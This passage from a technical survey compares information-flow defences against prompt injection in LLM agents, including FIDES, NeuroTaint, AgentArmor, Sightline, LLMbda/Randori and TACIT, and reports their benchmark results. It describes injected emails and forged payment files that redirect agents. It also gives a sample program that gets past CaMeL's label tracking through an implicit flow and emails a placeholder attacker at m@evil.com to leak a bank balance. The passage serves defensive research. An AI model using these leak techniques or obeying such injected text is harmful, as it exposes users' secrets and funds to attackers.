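FIDES flagged 54% of the scenarios with a flow and 53% of those without one, so its alarms were almost no evidence of influence. However, FIDES isn't designed to measure influence. If an agent reads an outside page and then writes an unrelated report, FIDES may raise an alarm that is correct under its trusted-action policy but counts as false on TaintBench.

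Of the 92 flows that FIDES missed, 40 were on four frameworks where it flagged nothing at all, which looks more like a problem with the test setup than with information-flow control. It also missed 23 of the 40 scenarios in which the source affected which tool the agent called or whether it called one. The labelled loop that Costa and colleagues describe should catch these, because it gives every later call the label of the whole context, but Cai and colleagues describe their FIDES baseline as reasoning over labels and known tool paths, which sounds weaker. The comparison across sessions is fairer, since FIDES loses its labels when a run ends. It found 5 of the 30 cross-session flows, and NeuroTaint found 28.

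NeuroTaint's own score also warrants some caution because the benchmark's categories closely match the detector's tests, with groups for exact markers, shared text, similar meaning, fragments and decisions. NeuroTaint wrongly flagged all 14 scenarios in which the sink's text only covered the same topic as the source. It also used a stricter similarity threshold, 0.95 instead of 0.60, for what the paper calls "safe-control policies". If these policies apply to scenarios without a flow, as the name suggests, the detector was less likely to raise an alarm in the scenarios where any alarm would be false.

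The two systems score almost the same on two benchmarks by other researchers. Both have an F1 of at least 0.99 on InjecAgent and an F1 of 0.760 on a filtered part of ToolEmu. These benchmarks label unsafe actions instead of influence, so the scores don't contradict the TaintBench result, but they give little reason to expect NeuroTaint to catch more attacks than the other system.

It is reasonable to compare FIDES and NeuroTaint on how well they identify the source behind an action, but not on how well they protect against attacks. FIDES decides before a call, when a false alarm can block a legitimate task and a miss can let an attack through. NeuroTaint reads the log after the email has been sent. F1 weights both kinds of error equally and doesn't account for this difference in timing.

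NeuroTaint looks useful for investigating past runs. It adds about a quarter of a second per run, and it narrowed the 400 scenarios to 203 for a second model to review. When Claude Opus 4.6 was the reviewer, it marked 179 of the 187 real flows as unsafe and raised no false alarms.

### Rebuilding a program from the trace

AgentArmor uses similar evidence before each call instead of after the run. Wang, Liu and colleagues (2025), in *AGENTARMOR*, treat the trace of an agent's run as if it were a program. The trace contains the prompts, the model's visible reasoning, its tool calls and their results. As the agent works, AgentArmor turns this record into three graphs:

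- A control-flow graph records the order of the steps and which earlier text led to each decision.
- A data-flow graph records where each argument came from and what data each tool touched.
- A program dependency graph combines the two.

Suppose an agent requests `git clone` after reading a project's README file. The log records the order of events, but not whether the agent is following the user's request or an instruction in the README. AgentArmor uses a separate model to infer this dependency and adds it as an edge in a graph. A registry then supplies security information about the tools and data, such as how sensitive a file is. A type system passes this information along the edges as security types and rejects the pending call if it breaks a policy.

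The type checker is ordinary program analysis, but it works on a graph that a model partly inferred. If the model attributes `git clone` to the user when the README prompted it, the checker will apply its rules correctly to a wrong graph and approve it. The AgentArmor paper acknowledges that an attacker could write an injection that misleads this second model as well. The graph also covers only one run, so AgentArmor loses the main advantage of static analysis, which is the ability to examine branches that the agent didn't take.

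According to the paper's abstract, AgentArmor reduces the attack success rate on AgentDojo to 3% and lowers utility by 1%. In the detailed results, the attack success rate falls from 16.66% to 1.16%, but utility falls from 63.5% to 56.8%, a larger loss than the abstract reports. The agent completes almost as many travel tasks as before, while its score on Slack tasks drops from 65.7% to 11.8%. So inferring dependencies doesn't reliably avoid the blocking that makes conservative labels unattractive.

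### Why a weak signal doesn't rule out influence

An estimator might do better by using information from inside the model. In a transformer, the design behind most LLMs, each position in the text draws information from earlier positions through a mechanism called attention. In *Sightline*, Xu, Li and colleagues (2026), two of whom helped design PRISM, prove that small changes to a placeholder can affect the output only through attention, so they have no effect if no later position attends to the placeholder.

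In practice, a model gives every placeholder at least a little attention, so an estimator would need to treat very weak attention as none. Xu and colleagues prove that this isn't safe. A placeholder's content helps determine how much attention it gets, so a model may give one value almost no attention but attend closely to another and change its answer. They construct a case where the attention is about two billionths, yet changing the placeholder's content flips the output. This resembles the implicit flow through a branch that a run doesn't take.

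Two other tests can miss inputs that influenced the output. The first measures how much a tiny change in an input changes the output's probability. When the model is almost certain of its answer, this effect is close to zero, even if the input determined that answer. The second test removes an input and checks whether the output changes. It fails when the same content appears twice, because the other copy remains.

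NeuroTaint's judge has this second weakness because NeuroTaint neutralises one source at a time. If two emails contain the same malicious command, the agent would still obey it if either email were neutralised. A judge that predicts this correctly will conclude that neither email influenced the agent.

Sightline therefore estimates whether an input had influence instead of trying to prove that it had none. It learns from labelled examples which patterns of attention are associated with real use, gives each placeholder a score, and sets a threshold that limits how often it misses a flow. To set the threshold, it scores one known flow from each of n groups of related code repositories and uses the k-th lowest score, where k = ⌊α(n + 1)⌋ and α is the permitted miss rate. With 1,000 groups and α = 1%, k is 10, so it drops only placeholders that score below the tenth-lowest known flow. The chance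 of missing a randomly drawn flow from a new group is then at most 10/1,001, or just under 1%.

At this setting, Sightline removed 43.9% to 65.6% of the unnecessary flows on four open models. In a separate test on AgentDojo, with a permitted miss rate of 5%, it removed half of the unnecessary labels, and a policy like FIDES's still stopped all 34 attack calls.

The bound holds only if new calls are exchangeable with the calls used to set the threshold, meaning that swapping a new call with any old one would not change the odds. This is a reasonable assumption for ordinary prompts from similar programs, but an attacker can choose text unlike any of them. None of the 34 attacks got through, but there is no sign in the test that their writers knew about Sightline.

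### Answering again from fewer inputs

Siddiqui, Gaonkar and colleagues (2024), in *Permissive Information-Flow Analysis for Large Language Models*, found a way to use an estimate without relying on it for security. Their system estimates which documents were enough to produce an answer, and then has the model answer again from those documents alone:

1. The model answers from all the documents.
2. The system picks a less restrictive label, such as "trusted", and leaves out every document that this label doesn't cover.
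3. It measures how likely the model would be to give the same answer from the remaining documents.
4. If the answer is still likely enough, the model writes a new answer from those documents. The system returns the new answer with the new label and discards the old one.

The third step uses perplexity, a measure of how unlikely a text is according to the model's probabilities. For an answer of n tokens (words or parts of words) with probabilities p₁ to pₙ, the perplexity is (p₁ × ... × pₙ)^(−1/n). The smaller set of documents is good enough if it raises the perplexity by at most a chosen tolerance λ. If every token has probability 0.8 with all the documents and 0.5 with the smaller set, the perplexity rises from 1.25 to 2. This rise of 0.75 is acceptable if λ is 1, but not if λ is 0.5.

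In one example, a user asks how many people live in New York. A trusted page gives 8.4 million and an untrusted page gives about 8 million. The model can answer from the trusted page alone, so the answer counts as trusted.

The same method could let the office assistant schedule the Friday meeting that the labelled loop blocked. If the system removed the outside email and queried the model again, the model would probably still request the meeting, because the user asked for it. That request would be trusted because the model no longer had the email containing the injected command. The summary would stay untrusted because it needs the email.

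An attacker may fool the estimate, but this doesn't put untrusted text into a trusted answer. If the system wrongly decides that a document didn't matter, the model writes the new answer without that document, so the answer may be worse but the document can't influence it. This guarantee assumes that the inputs are labeled correctly. Siddiqui and colleagues also assume that adding documents never makes the original answer less likely, but they need this only to show that the search finds every least restrictive label. If that second assumption is false, the system may keep a stricter label than necessary, but the guarantee still holds.

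The guarantee covers the text of the answer, but the choice of label still depends on all the documents. Suppose a public document says that a project is on schedule, and a secret one says either the same or that the company has cancelled it. If the two agree, the public document is enough and the assistant may send its answer to a supplier. If they disagree, the answer keeps its secret label and the assistant sends nothing. A supplier who knows how the system works can learn about the cancellation from not receiving an answer. Regenerating the answer doesn't remove this implicit flow.

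Siddiqui and colleagues tested the search on questions with 14 documents each, so it had to find the right combinations among 2¹⁴ = 16,384. It found exactly the right set of labels for 86% of the questions. When asked which documents had mattered, Llama 2 70B, the larger of their two models, was right for only 13%. On news articles, the search with the smaller Llama 2 model improved 57% of the labels that could be improved, but 23% of these improvements left out a source that the reference answer needed. These are old models, and a current one would probably be better at naming its own sources. The method needs at least one extra scoring pass and, when it finds a better label, a second answer.

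### Removing labels and adding alarms

The other estimators provide evidence about influence, but it is risky to use that evidence to remove a label from an answer the model has already written. Even if an estimator had only a 1% chance of missing each attack, an attacker with 100 independent attempts would have a 1 − 0.99¹⁰⁰ ≈ 63% chance of getting at least one past it. Someone who knew how the estimator worked could probably do better. Sightline's bound can help decide how many false alarms to remove from an analysis of ordinary programs, but it doesn't bound what an attacker can achieve.

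An estimator that only adds alarms can't weaken an existing guarantee. A developer could let FIDES block calls based on conservative labels and run NeuroTaint on the logs to look for flows the labels missed. TaintBench includes ten scenarios in which the data comes from a source that seems trusted or has no label. NeuroTaint found the flow in all ten, and FIDES in one.

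## The LLMbda calculus and a proof that covers generated code

Conservative labels give a guarantee only if the software that tracks them misses no flow. Costa and colleagues prove that FIDES misses no explicit flow in one particular loop. Their proof allows any planner and any set of tools, but the loop can only query the model, call a tool or finish. When an agent writes and runs programs, as CaMeL does, the model also supplies branches, loops and variables, and information can leak through each of them.

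One could try to fit such an agent into FIDES by adding a tool that runs a program. FIDES labels a tool's result according to what the tool may read, which somebody has to declare in advance. For a tool that runs arbitrary code, the only safe declaration is that it may read all the data the agent can reach. The policies would then block most of what the agent tried to do next.

CaMeL's interpreter instead tracks labels inside the generated program, but it has no comparable proof. Garby and colleagues found several ways for data to lose its label in the interpreter. In the simplest, a program inserts an untrusted value into a string template and the interpreter treats the resulting string as trusted. Two others are harder to spot.

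### The branch that didn't run

Suppose again that an attacker wants an agent to email "rich!" to an outsider if an account balance exceeds a threshold. CaMeL blocks the direct version, where the code sends the email inside a branch that depends on the balance. Its interpreter keeps a program-counter label, written pc, which is the join of the labels of all the conditions that led to the current line. Inside that branch, pc is secret, so the interpreter does not send the email.

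The following program gets around this with two extra variables:

```
tmp = True
rich = True
if balance > threshold:
    tmp = False
if tmp:
    rich = False
if rich:
    send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

| Line | Balance above the threshold | Balance below the threshold |
|---|---|---|
| `tmp = False` | runs, and `tmp` becomes secret | skipped, so `tmp` stays true and public |
| `rich = False` | skipped, so `rich` stays true and public | runs, and `rich` becomes false but stays public |
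| `send_email(...)` | runs | skipped |

In both runs `rich` ends up with a public label, but its value reveals whether the balance is above the threshold. The interpreter raises a variable's label when an assignment runs in a secret context. With a high balance, the assignment that should have made `rich` secret never runs.

Fenton described this problem in 1974, and later researchers rediscovered it. An injected email can't normally put these lines into a CaMeL program, because the planner writes the program before it reads any email. The leak could still matter if the user pastes an attacker's text into the request, or if the planner happens to write a program with this structure.

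### No sensitive upgrades

A rule called no-sensitive-upgrade stops this leak. Before each assignment to a variable x, the interpreter checks that

pc ⊑ label(x)

where ⊑ means "may flow to". If the check fails, the program stops. Otherwise the variable's new label is the join of pc and the label of the assigned value. In the program above, a high balance makes pc secret at `tmp = False` while `tmp` is still public, so the program stops there. With a low balance, it runs to the end and sends nothing. The outsider gets no email either way. Austin and Flanagan (2009), in *Efficient purely-dynamic information flow analysis*, use a dynamic check to guarantee noninterference without any static analysis.

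Instead of stopping the program, the interpreter could make `tmp` secret, as CaMeL does, but that protects `tmp` only in the run where the assignment happens. Austin and Flanagan's *Permissive Dynamic Information Flow Analysis* calls such a variable partially leaked, because its label would still be public in a run that skips the assignment.

The rule also stops harmless programs. Bichhawat, Rajani and colleagues (2015), in *Generalizing Permissive-Upgrade in Dynamic Information Flow Analysis*, give an example of a program that changes a variable in a secret branch and then never reads it. A more permissive rule allows the assignment, marks the variable as partially leaked and stops the program only if it later tries to use the variable, for instance in a condition. Under this rule, the program in the balance example would stop at `if tmp`.

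A static analyser examines both branches, so it would mark `tmp` and then `rich` as secret whichever branch runs, and reject the program because of the email. It would have no reason to reject a program that never uses the variable again. Russo and Sabelfeld argue in *Dynamic vs. Static Flow-Sensitive Security Analysis* that purely dynamic monitors face a fundamental limit once a variable's label can change during a run.

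### One bit per retry

The no-sensitive-upgrade rule closes the first leak, but the balance still affects whether the program finishes. Anyone who can tell that the program stopped early learns that the balance is high. Most information-flow systems tolerate this kind of leak because it usually reveals only one bit per run.

CaMeL runs its interpreter inside an ordinary Python loop that retries after a failure, and the interpreter doesn't track labels in that loop. Each attempt starts with clean labels, even though it runs only because the previous one failed. A program that adapts between attempts could therefore test a different bit of a secret each time. CaMeL censors the error messages it passes from one attempt to the next, which should reduce the leak, but Garby and colleagues point out that this gives no formal guarantee.

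### A language that includes the conversation

Garby and colleagues designed the programming language LLMbda so that they could prove a guarantee for every program in it, including programs that generate code. It extends the lambda calculus, a minimal language in which programs consist of functions and their applications. Every value has a label, which in the simplest version is a subset of {U, S}, where U means untrusted and S means secret. The conversation with the model has a label too. Four operations act on it:

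- `send e` adds the value of e to the conversation and joins its label into the conversation's label.
- `recv` gets a reply from the model, adds it to the conversation, parses it as code and runs that code.
- `fork e` runs e with a temporary copy of the conversation, then restores the original and keeps only the result.
- `clear` empties the conversation.

The shorthand `@e` sends a prompt and receives the reply. The `assert` operation stops the program unless a value's label may flow to a given label, and tools use it to enforce policies.

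When `recv` runs code from a reply, it sets pc to the label of the conversation that produced the reply. Suppose an untrusted email persuades the model to write a program that transfers money. The email makes the conversation untrusted, so everything the program computes is untrusted too, and a payment tool that asserts that the recipient is trusted will block the transfer. Nobody has to inspect the program or recognise it as malicious. The proof makes no assumption about the parser, so it holds for any code an attacker can get the model to write.

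The no-sensitive-upgrade rule also applies to the conversation, because `send` requires pc ⊑ label(conversation). In one of Garby and colleagues' examples, a program tells the model that x is false. If a secret is true, the program then tells the model that x is true. Finally, it asks for the value of x. When the secret is true, the interpreter stops the program at the second message.

If a program sends a record with several fields, the conversation takes on every field's label. Operations that build strings also join the labels of their parts, so a string template can't remove a label as it could in CaMeL.

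The quarantined model from the dual-LLM pattern now takes one line, shown here in simplified notation:

```
quarantine(prompt) = fork (clear; @prompt)
```

The untrusted text enters only the temporary copy of the conversation. The answer comes back labeled untrusted, and the main conversation stays trusted. A developer can therefore write the basic agent loop, the dual-LLM pattern or a CaMeL-style planner in the same language, and the same theorem covers all of them.

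Garby and colleagues tried two of these designs on an email from Bob. The user wanted to remind Bob of a meeting, but the email contained an injected postscript with a request for a cancellation. With a single conversation, GPT-4o sent the cancellation. A planner that wrote its program first and used `quarantine` sent the reminder. Its `send_email` tool asserts that the subject and body are trusted, so if a message passes the check, the email's text can't have influenced either of them. The check doesn't cover the recipient's address, which came from the email.

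### Noninterference with random replies

The main theorem is termination-insensitive probabilistic noninterference, or TIPNI. It concerns an observer at level m, who can see every value whose label may flow to m. Two starting points look alike to this observer (written ~m) if they differ only in things the observer can't see. Since the model's replies are random, each starting point leads to a probability distribution over results. Strict noninterference would require the observer to see the same distribution from any two starting points that look alike.

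TIPNI is weaker because a run may never produce a result. It may loop forever, or a check may stop it. The probabilities of the results can therefore add up to less than 1. Two such distributions μ and ν are compatible, written μ ⌣ ν, if some third distribution ω satisfies

μ(q) ≤ ω(q) and ν(q) ≤ ω(q) for every result q, with Σ ω(q) ≤ 1.

For a conversation C and a program e, let ⟦pc ⊢ C, e⟧ₘ be the distribution of results as the observer sees them. The theorem states, for every level m:

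If C₀ ~m C₁ and e₀ ~m e₁, then ⟦pc ⊢ C₀, e₀⟧ₘ ⌣ ⟦pc ⊢ C₁, e₁⟧ₘ.

Suppose a program prints "yes" with probability 0.5 and "no" with probability 0.3 when a secret bit is 0, and prints each with probability 0.4 when the bit is 1. Either way, it fails to finish with probability 0.2. The smallest ω takes the larger probability for each result, giving 0.5 + 0.4 = 0.9. This total does not exceed 1, so the distributions are compatible. If the program always finished, each distribution would add up to 1, and they would be compatible only if they were identical. In general, the statistical distance between two compatible distributions (half the sum of the absolute differences) is at most the average probability of not finishing. Here the distance is 0.1 and the bound is 0.2.

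The weaker definition permits some programs that can reveal a secret. A program could ask the model for a random digit, then print it if it matches a secret digit and loop forever if it doesn't. Any digit it prints is the secret one, yet the program satisfies TIPNI because it finishes only one time in ten. With a six-digit code, it would finish about one time in a million. But somebody who kept restarting it would eventually get the code, so running LLMbda inside an ordinary retry loop would bring back CaMeL's second leak.

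### How the proof works

The proof uses a modified version of the language's rules. A program runs normally under these rules until it reaches a computation whose label the observer can't see. It then skips that computation and puts an empty record in its place.

Because the modified rules ignore everything hidden, they give the same distribution ω for any two starting points that look alike to the observer. They also produce each visible result at least as often as the real rules do, since a skipped computation can't loop forever or fail a check. If μ₀ and μ₁ are the real distributions, then

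μ₀ ≤ ω₀ = ω₁ ≥ μ₁,

which is what compatibility requires. Skipping is safe because a hidden computation can't change a public conversation, thanks to the check in `send`.

Smith and Alpízar earlier proved a similar theorem for a simple language by deleting the hidden parts from a program's source. That method doesn't work here because some of the code doesn't exist until the model writes it. Garby and colleagues instead deleted the hidden parts from the run, so their result covers all possible runs without requiring all the code in advance.

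The proof is checked in Lean, a proof-checking language, and the interpreter is also written in Lean, so the theorems apply to the same interpreter that runs the agent. The proof does not cover the code that sends requests to the model over the network.

### What the proof takes for granted

The theorem covers a model that an attacker fully controls, but it relies on several other things:

- **Correct labels on sources.** If a developer forgets to mark web pages as untrusted, the theorem treats their contents as trusted.
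- **Checks at sinks.** Labels don't stop a payment by themselves. The payment tool has to test them.
- **All data sources inside the program.** Garby and colleagues represent the outside world as a record that tools read and update. They list this as a limitation, since a real mail server or bank would be outside the program.
- **Independent replies.** The proof that the interpreter is correct assumes that each reply depends only on the conversation sent with the request. If a model provider carried information over from other conversations, `fork` and `clear` would no longer isolate anything.

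*GIF* (2026) argues that noninterference is too strong a target for agents. Any token can weakly affect any later one, so an analysis that requires zero flow is either too conservative or too expensive to compute. *GIF* proposes measuring how much information flows instead. LLMbda and FIDES both take the conservative option. An LLMbda program can use `fork` to limit the effects of this conservatism, but some tasks also need an untrusted value to be treated as trusted.

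### Endorsing a value

Suppose the assistant sorts incoming emails and puts the category in the subject line of its reply. The category comes from an untrusted email, so `send_email` rejects it. LLMbda's `endorse` operation relabels it. An endorsed value gets the label

pc ⊔ ⟨integrity of the target label, confidentiality of the value⟩

where ⊔ is the join. The join with pc prevents an attacker from using `endorse` directly. Code generated from an untrusted conversation may contain the operation, but the result stays untrusted.

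An attacker who can only choose among n fixed categories controls at most log2 n bits, as with the fixed lists in FIDES. Written in Python style, a safe wrapper looks like this:

```
def bounded_endorse(v):
    w = endorse(TRUSTED, v)
    if w in ["invoice", "complaint", "meeting", "general"]:
        return w
    return v
```

The function has to endorse the value before checking it. A condition that reads `v` depends on untrusted data, so pc would become untrusted and an endorsement inside that branch would have no effect. If the value isn't on the list, the function returns the original, which is still untrusted. The list must be fixed in advance, because otherwise n could grow. Garby and colleagues have not yet formally proved the bound for this wrapper.

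A theorem called insulated TIPNI shows that endorsement can't leak secrets. It splits each label into an integrity part and a confidentiality part, and considers observers from whom values are hidden only by the confidentiality part. For every such observer, TIPNI holds whatever untrusted inputs the attacker chooses and whatever the program endorses. This is because the formula takes the confidentiality part from the value itself, so if a program endorses a secret password, the password becomes trusted but stays secret. A careless endorsement might let an attacker redirect a payment, but it can't make a secret value pass a check for public data.

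Endorsements can undermine integrity more seriously when they form a chain. Suppose a program endorses some outside text and sends it to the model, which writes code based on it. The conversation counts as trusted, so the new code runs as trusted and can make effective endorsements of its own. Garby and colleagues describe a wrapper that marks each endorsed value and refuses to endorse a marked value again. The wrapper requires no changes to the language's rules, but it works only if the parser rejects direct uses of `endorse` in generated code.

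### Randori practises before it acts

To test the language, Garby and colleagues used it to write an agent called Randori. Like CaMeL, Randori has a quarantined model and a planner that writes a program. Models often make mistakes in a language they have never seen, so the planner needs several attempts. If those attempts used real data, an error in a program that had read an untrusted file would taint the conversation, and every later program would be untrusted.

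Randori avoids this by practising on invented data:

1. The planner writes a program for the user's request.
2. Randori runs it on a mock bank account, where `send_money` does nothing and `read_file` always returns the same placeholder text.
3. If the program fails, the planner sees the error and tries again. Since the mock data is trusted, so is the error message.
4. The planner writes a final version, which runs once on the real data.

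No retry depends on real data, so this also avoids the leak in CaMeL's retry loop. But Randori doesn't raise label errors during rehearsal, so a program can pass the rehearsal and then break a policy in the real run, which has no retries.

The planner writes any endorsements at this stage too, before it has read outside data, so an injected instruction can't ask for one.

### Results on the banking tasks

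Garby and colleagues ran each of AgentDojo's 16 banking tasks three times without attacks, giving 48 runs per model. They also ran each of the 144 task-attack pairs three times, giving 432 attacked runs per model. For comparison, they reran CaMeL with its policies on and off. Some of CaMeL's attacked runs did not complete, so the last column includes only those that did.

| System | Model | Tasks completed without attacks, of 48 | Successful attacks |
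|---|---|---|---|
| Randori | GPT-5.2 | 36 (75.0%) | 2 of 432 |
| Randori | Qwen3.7-plus | 36 (75.0%) | 0 of 432 |
| Randori | MiMo-v2.5 | 31 (64.6%) | 0 of 432 |
| Randori, no endorsement | Qwen3.7-plus | 30 (62.5%) | 0 of 432 |
| Randori, no endorsement | MiMo-v2.5 | 26 (54.2%) | 0 of 432 |
| CaMeL, policies off | GPT-5.2 | 32 (66.7%) | 1 of 240 |
| CaMeL, policies off | MiMo-v2.5 | 34 (70.8%) | 4 of 382 |
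| CaMeL, policies on | GPT-5.2 | 18 (37.5%) | 0 of 231 |
| CaMeL, policies on | MiMo-v2.5 | 18 (37.5%) | 0 of 357 |

Randori, which always checks labels, completes about as many tasks as CaMeL without its policies and far more than CaMeL with them. Because there are only 16 different tasks, the margins of error are roughly 19 to 27 percentage points either way, so the smaller differences between rows mean little.

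The gap between Randori and CaMeL with policies is large, but the proof is probably not the main reason. Endorsement accounts for some of it. With MiMo-v2.5, Randori completed 13 more runs than CaMeL with policies, and it lost only five of those when it couldn't endorse anything. Looser policies may well explain much of the rest, since Randori enforces only a subset of CaMeL's policies, and Garby and colleagues acknowledge that theirs are less strict.

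Endorsement helps on three tasks in which the user asks the agent to read a file and act on it. Randori can gain only so much from endorsement, because two of these tasks are hard for it even with endorsement.

The attack results provide little evidence about the value of the proof. Even with its policies off, CaMeL resisted all but five of 622 completed attacks, and two of those five used the kind of program that follows a file's instructions. With its policies on, CaMeL stopped every attack despite the leaks through the skipped branch and the retry loop, but none of the attacks was designed to exploit either leak.

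### The two attacks that worked

Both successful attacks on Randori involved the same task and injection. The user asks the agent to read a text file and make the payment it describes, but the attacker has replaced the file's contents with a different payment request. GPT-5.2's planner wrote a program that endorsed details from the file, so the payment tool accepted them. Without endorsement, Randori blocks this attack.

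Both successes in the 1,296 runs came from the three runs in which GPT-5.2 faced this particular combination. The low overall rate is a poor guide to the risk, because an attacker who knows that an agent pays bills from files would choose this attack.

No theorem failed in these runs. Insulated TIPNI doesn't apply because it protects secrets, and the attacker wanted money. The log2 n bound doesn't apply either, because an account number isn't a choice from a short list. A wrapper that required a short list would stop the attack, but it would also stop payment of a genuine bill. The wrapper against chains would let the attack through, since the planner made a single endorsement in a trusted program.

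Garby and colleagues consider such attacks out of scope for information-flow control, because the user told the agent to trust the file and labels can't distinguish a real bill from a forged one. This is fair when the task is to pay whatever the file says. However, the planner decides which values to endorse, and Randori doesn't limit it to cases where the user has clearly delegated that trust. A less careful planner could endorse an account number from a web page that the user never mentioned, and the payment tool would accept that too. Letting the planner endorse freely therefore makes the integrity guarantee depend on the model's judgement, which it doesn't for plans without endorsements.

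LLMbda at least makes these decisions easy to find, because each one appears as an explicit `endorse` in the program before it runs. A developer could reject plans that endorse a payment recipient, or have the user confirm the account number once the program has read it from the file. Garby and colleagues leave the static analysis of such plans to future work.

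## TACIT and type-checking the code an agent writes

LLMbda checks labels while generated code runs. *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* (Odersky, Zhao and colleagues, 2026) describes TACIT ("Tracked Agent Capabilities In Types"), which checks the code first. The agent writes short Scala programs instead of requesting single tool calls, and a compiler statically checks each program before it runs.

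### One snippet at a time

TACIT is an MCP server, so an existing agent such as Claude Code can connect to it without modification. Each step works like this:

1. The agent submits a snippet of Scala as the argument of a tool call.
2. The compiler checks the snippet's types. If it finds an error, the agent gets the error message and can try again.
3. If the snippet passes, TACIT runs it and returns the output.
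4. The agent reads the output and writes the next snippet.

This is still the basic agent loop, so no analyser can determine in advance which snippets the model will write. But once a snippet is written, it is ordinary source code with fixed control flow. The compiler's result holds regardless of what is in the files and web pages that the snippet reads, and it covers branches that the run will skip.

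Variables can carry over from one snippet to the next and keep their types, so the compiler can check each new snippet against the variables from earlier ones. If every snippet has to satisfy some property, the property holds for the whole run, regardless of how many snippets the agent writes or what text led it to write them.

Unlike CaMeL's planner, TACIT's agent can look at an ordinary result and then decide what to do next.

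### Capabilities and capture sets

An object capability is a program value that code must hold to perform some effect, such as writing to a file. Code cannot forge a capability and can get one only from other code that already has it. CaMeL uses the word "capabilities" differently, to mean labels.

In TACIT, a `FileSystem` capability gives access to one folder and everything inside it. Calling `access("notes.txt")` on it returns a handle for a single file, and that handle is also a capability.

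Older capability languages rely on checks during the run. Scala 3 has an experimental feature called capture checking, which records capabilities in types. If `f` is a file handle, the function `s => f.write(s)` has this type:

```
String ->{f} Unit
```

The function takes a string, returns no useful value (`Unit`) and may use `f`. The part in braces is its capture set, which is an over-approximation because the function might use `f` only in a branch that never runs. A pure function has an empty capture set, so its type here would be `String -> Unit`. A program may use a pure function where the type permits capabilities, but not the other way round.

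When a program passes functions around as values, an analyser building a call graph has to work out which function each call might run. The capture checker needs only the function's type, which includes a capture set listing what the function may use, so it can check each part of a program separately. Agents can therefore define their own functions and use recursion, which CaMeL's restricted Python doesn't allow. *LACUNA* (2026), which checks agent code against the surrounding program, also uses Scala's capture checking.

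A snippet gets access to files by opening a block:

```
requestFileSystem("/project") {
  // code here can use files under /project
}
```

The capability is valid only inside the block. The block's result type cannot mention a capability that the block created, so the compiler rejects a snippet for returning a function that uses the capability later. In one of Odersky and colleagues' test runs, an agent tried to return a list of file handles from a block and got a compiler error for this reason.

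### Two programs and a confidential budget

The operator of TACIT can mark certain paths as classified. A program that reads a classified file gets a `Classified[String]`, a wrapper with no method that would let the agent take the string out. The agent can work on the contents through `map`, which applies a function to them and wraps the result again:

```
def map[B](op: T -> B): Classified[B]
```

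The plain arrow in `T -> B` means that `map` accepts only pure functions.

Suppose the user asks for a summary of a confidential budget. The compiler accepts this program:

```
requestFileSystem("/project") {
  val budget = readClassified("secrets/budget.txt")
  val summary = chat(budget.map(s => s"Summarise this budget:\n$s"))
  writeClassified("secrets/summary.txt", summary)
}
```

The function inside `map` only builds a longer string, so it is pure. `chat` sends that string to a second model, which the operator trusts and can run locally, then wraps the answer. The agent's own model, which usually runs on another company's servers, never receives the budget or the summary.

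The compiler rejects this one:

```
requestFileSystem("/project") {
  val notes = access("notes.txt")
  val budget = readClassified("secrets/budget.txt")
  budget.map(s => notes.write(s))
}
```

The function has the type `String ->{notes} Unit`, but `map` requires `String -> Unit`. The agent gets an error that `notes` cannot flow into an empty capture set. None of the snippet runs, including the part that reads the budget.

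A function can pass on what it reads only through its result or an effect. `map` puts the result back in the wrapper, and every effect that matters is supposed to need a capability, which a pure function doesn't have. Odersky and colleagues use "local purity" for the ability to enforce purity in one part of a program while the rest still has effects.

Local purity also stops implicit flows, such as the "rich!" email that reveals a bank balance. If sending email needs a capability, the compiler rejects the call inside `map`, whichever branch contains it. Outside `map`, comparing the balance with a threshold yields a `Classified[Boolean]`, which an `if` statement can't use. The two-variable trick that defeats CaMeL's interpreter also fails, because changing a variable defined outside the function counts as an effect.

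An ordinary sandbox would not catch such leaks because it limits only which files and servers a process can reach. This agent has permission to read the budget and to contact its model, so the sandbox would not stop it from sending the budget's contents to the model.

### Safe mode

Full Scala has features that would let a snippet get rid of a capture set. A type cast could present the function that writes to `notes` as a pure one, and reflection could find a file-writing method by name. Scala's *Safe Mode*, part of the language's documentation, describes a subset for untrusted code with six restrictions:

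- no unchecked type casts or pattern matches
- nothing from the module `caps.unsafe`
- no annotations that switch off checks
- no reflection while the program runs
- capture checking always on, including for changes to variables
- no global objects unless they are themselves safe

Without the last restriction, a snippet could ignore TACIT's library and call Java's own file functions.

Library code sometimes needs the unsafe features internally. A programmer can mark such a module `@assumeSafe`, and the compiler then lets snippets call it without checking the module's code. The Scala documentation gives the example of a mail module that asks the user for confirmation before it sends anything. The agent can call this module but not the unrestricted mailer underneath. The compiler would still accept the module if the programmer forgot the confirmation step.

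TACIT did not initially use the compiler to enforce all of this. According to the README in lampepfl's *TACIT*, the project's code repository, a separate validator searched each snippet for forbidden patterns because the compiler's safe mode was still under development. A newer README, reproduced in Glama's *TACIT*, still includes the validator but also describes a setting for safe mode, listed as on by default. This is an improvement because a list of forbidden patterns protects only against tricks that somebody thought of.

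### The parts that have to work

The guarantee depends on the compiler, TACIT's library, the runtime that executes the snippets and the trusted second model, but not on the agent's model, which Odersky and colleagues treat as possibly cooperating with an attacker. The second model must not remember earlier requests, or it might repeat part of the budget in an answer to an unclassified question.

The reusable part of the library is about 1,000 lines, short enough for a careful person to review. The compiler is much larger, and capture checking is still experimental. Proofs exist for simplified versions of the language. *Classifying Capabilities (Extended Version)* (2026) proves type and effect safety for one of them in Lean. *System Capybara* (2026) proves further properties for another, but leaves out classes and exceptions, which the real compiler has to handle. Odersky and colleagues acknowledge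 that there is still no proof that safe mode provides what TACIT needs. LLMbda is ahead on this point because its theorems describe the interpreter that runs the agent.

A configuration mistake could also undo the protection. Coding agents come with their own tools for files, shell commands and web access, which lampepfl recommends switching off. If a developer leaves the shell tool on, the agent can use it to read the budget without submitting any Scala.

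### What the types leave to run time

The type of a snippet shows that it may use files, but not which files, because the program may compute a path while it runs. TACIT therefore divides the work between the compiler and the library:

| Subject | The compiler settles | The library checks during the run |
|---|---|---|
| Files | Whether the code holds a file capability and keeps it inside its block | Whether the path is inside the permitted folder |
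| Commands and servers | Whether the code holds the permission | Whether this command or host is on the list |
| Classified data | Whether the function applied to it is pure | Whether this path is classified |
| Exceptions | That they carry no capabilities | That their contents don't reach the agent |
| Printing | That a wrapped value stays wrapped | That the agent sees only a redacted form |

If the accepted program wrote its summary to `public/summary.txt`, it would still compile. The library would then stop it with a security exception, because `writeClassified` works only on classified paths.

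A snippet names the commands and hosts it wants, for instance with `requestNetwork(Set("api.example.com"))`, and the compiler doesn't check whether the request is reasonable. These lists therefore restrict the agent only if someone else sets an outer limit. In the newer version, the operator can do this, and a command or host then has to be on both the operator's list and the snippet's. By default, folders are limited to the directory in which the server runs, but hosts have no outer limit.

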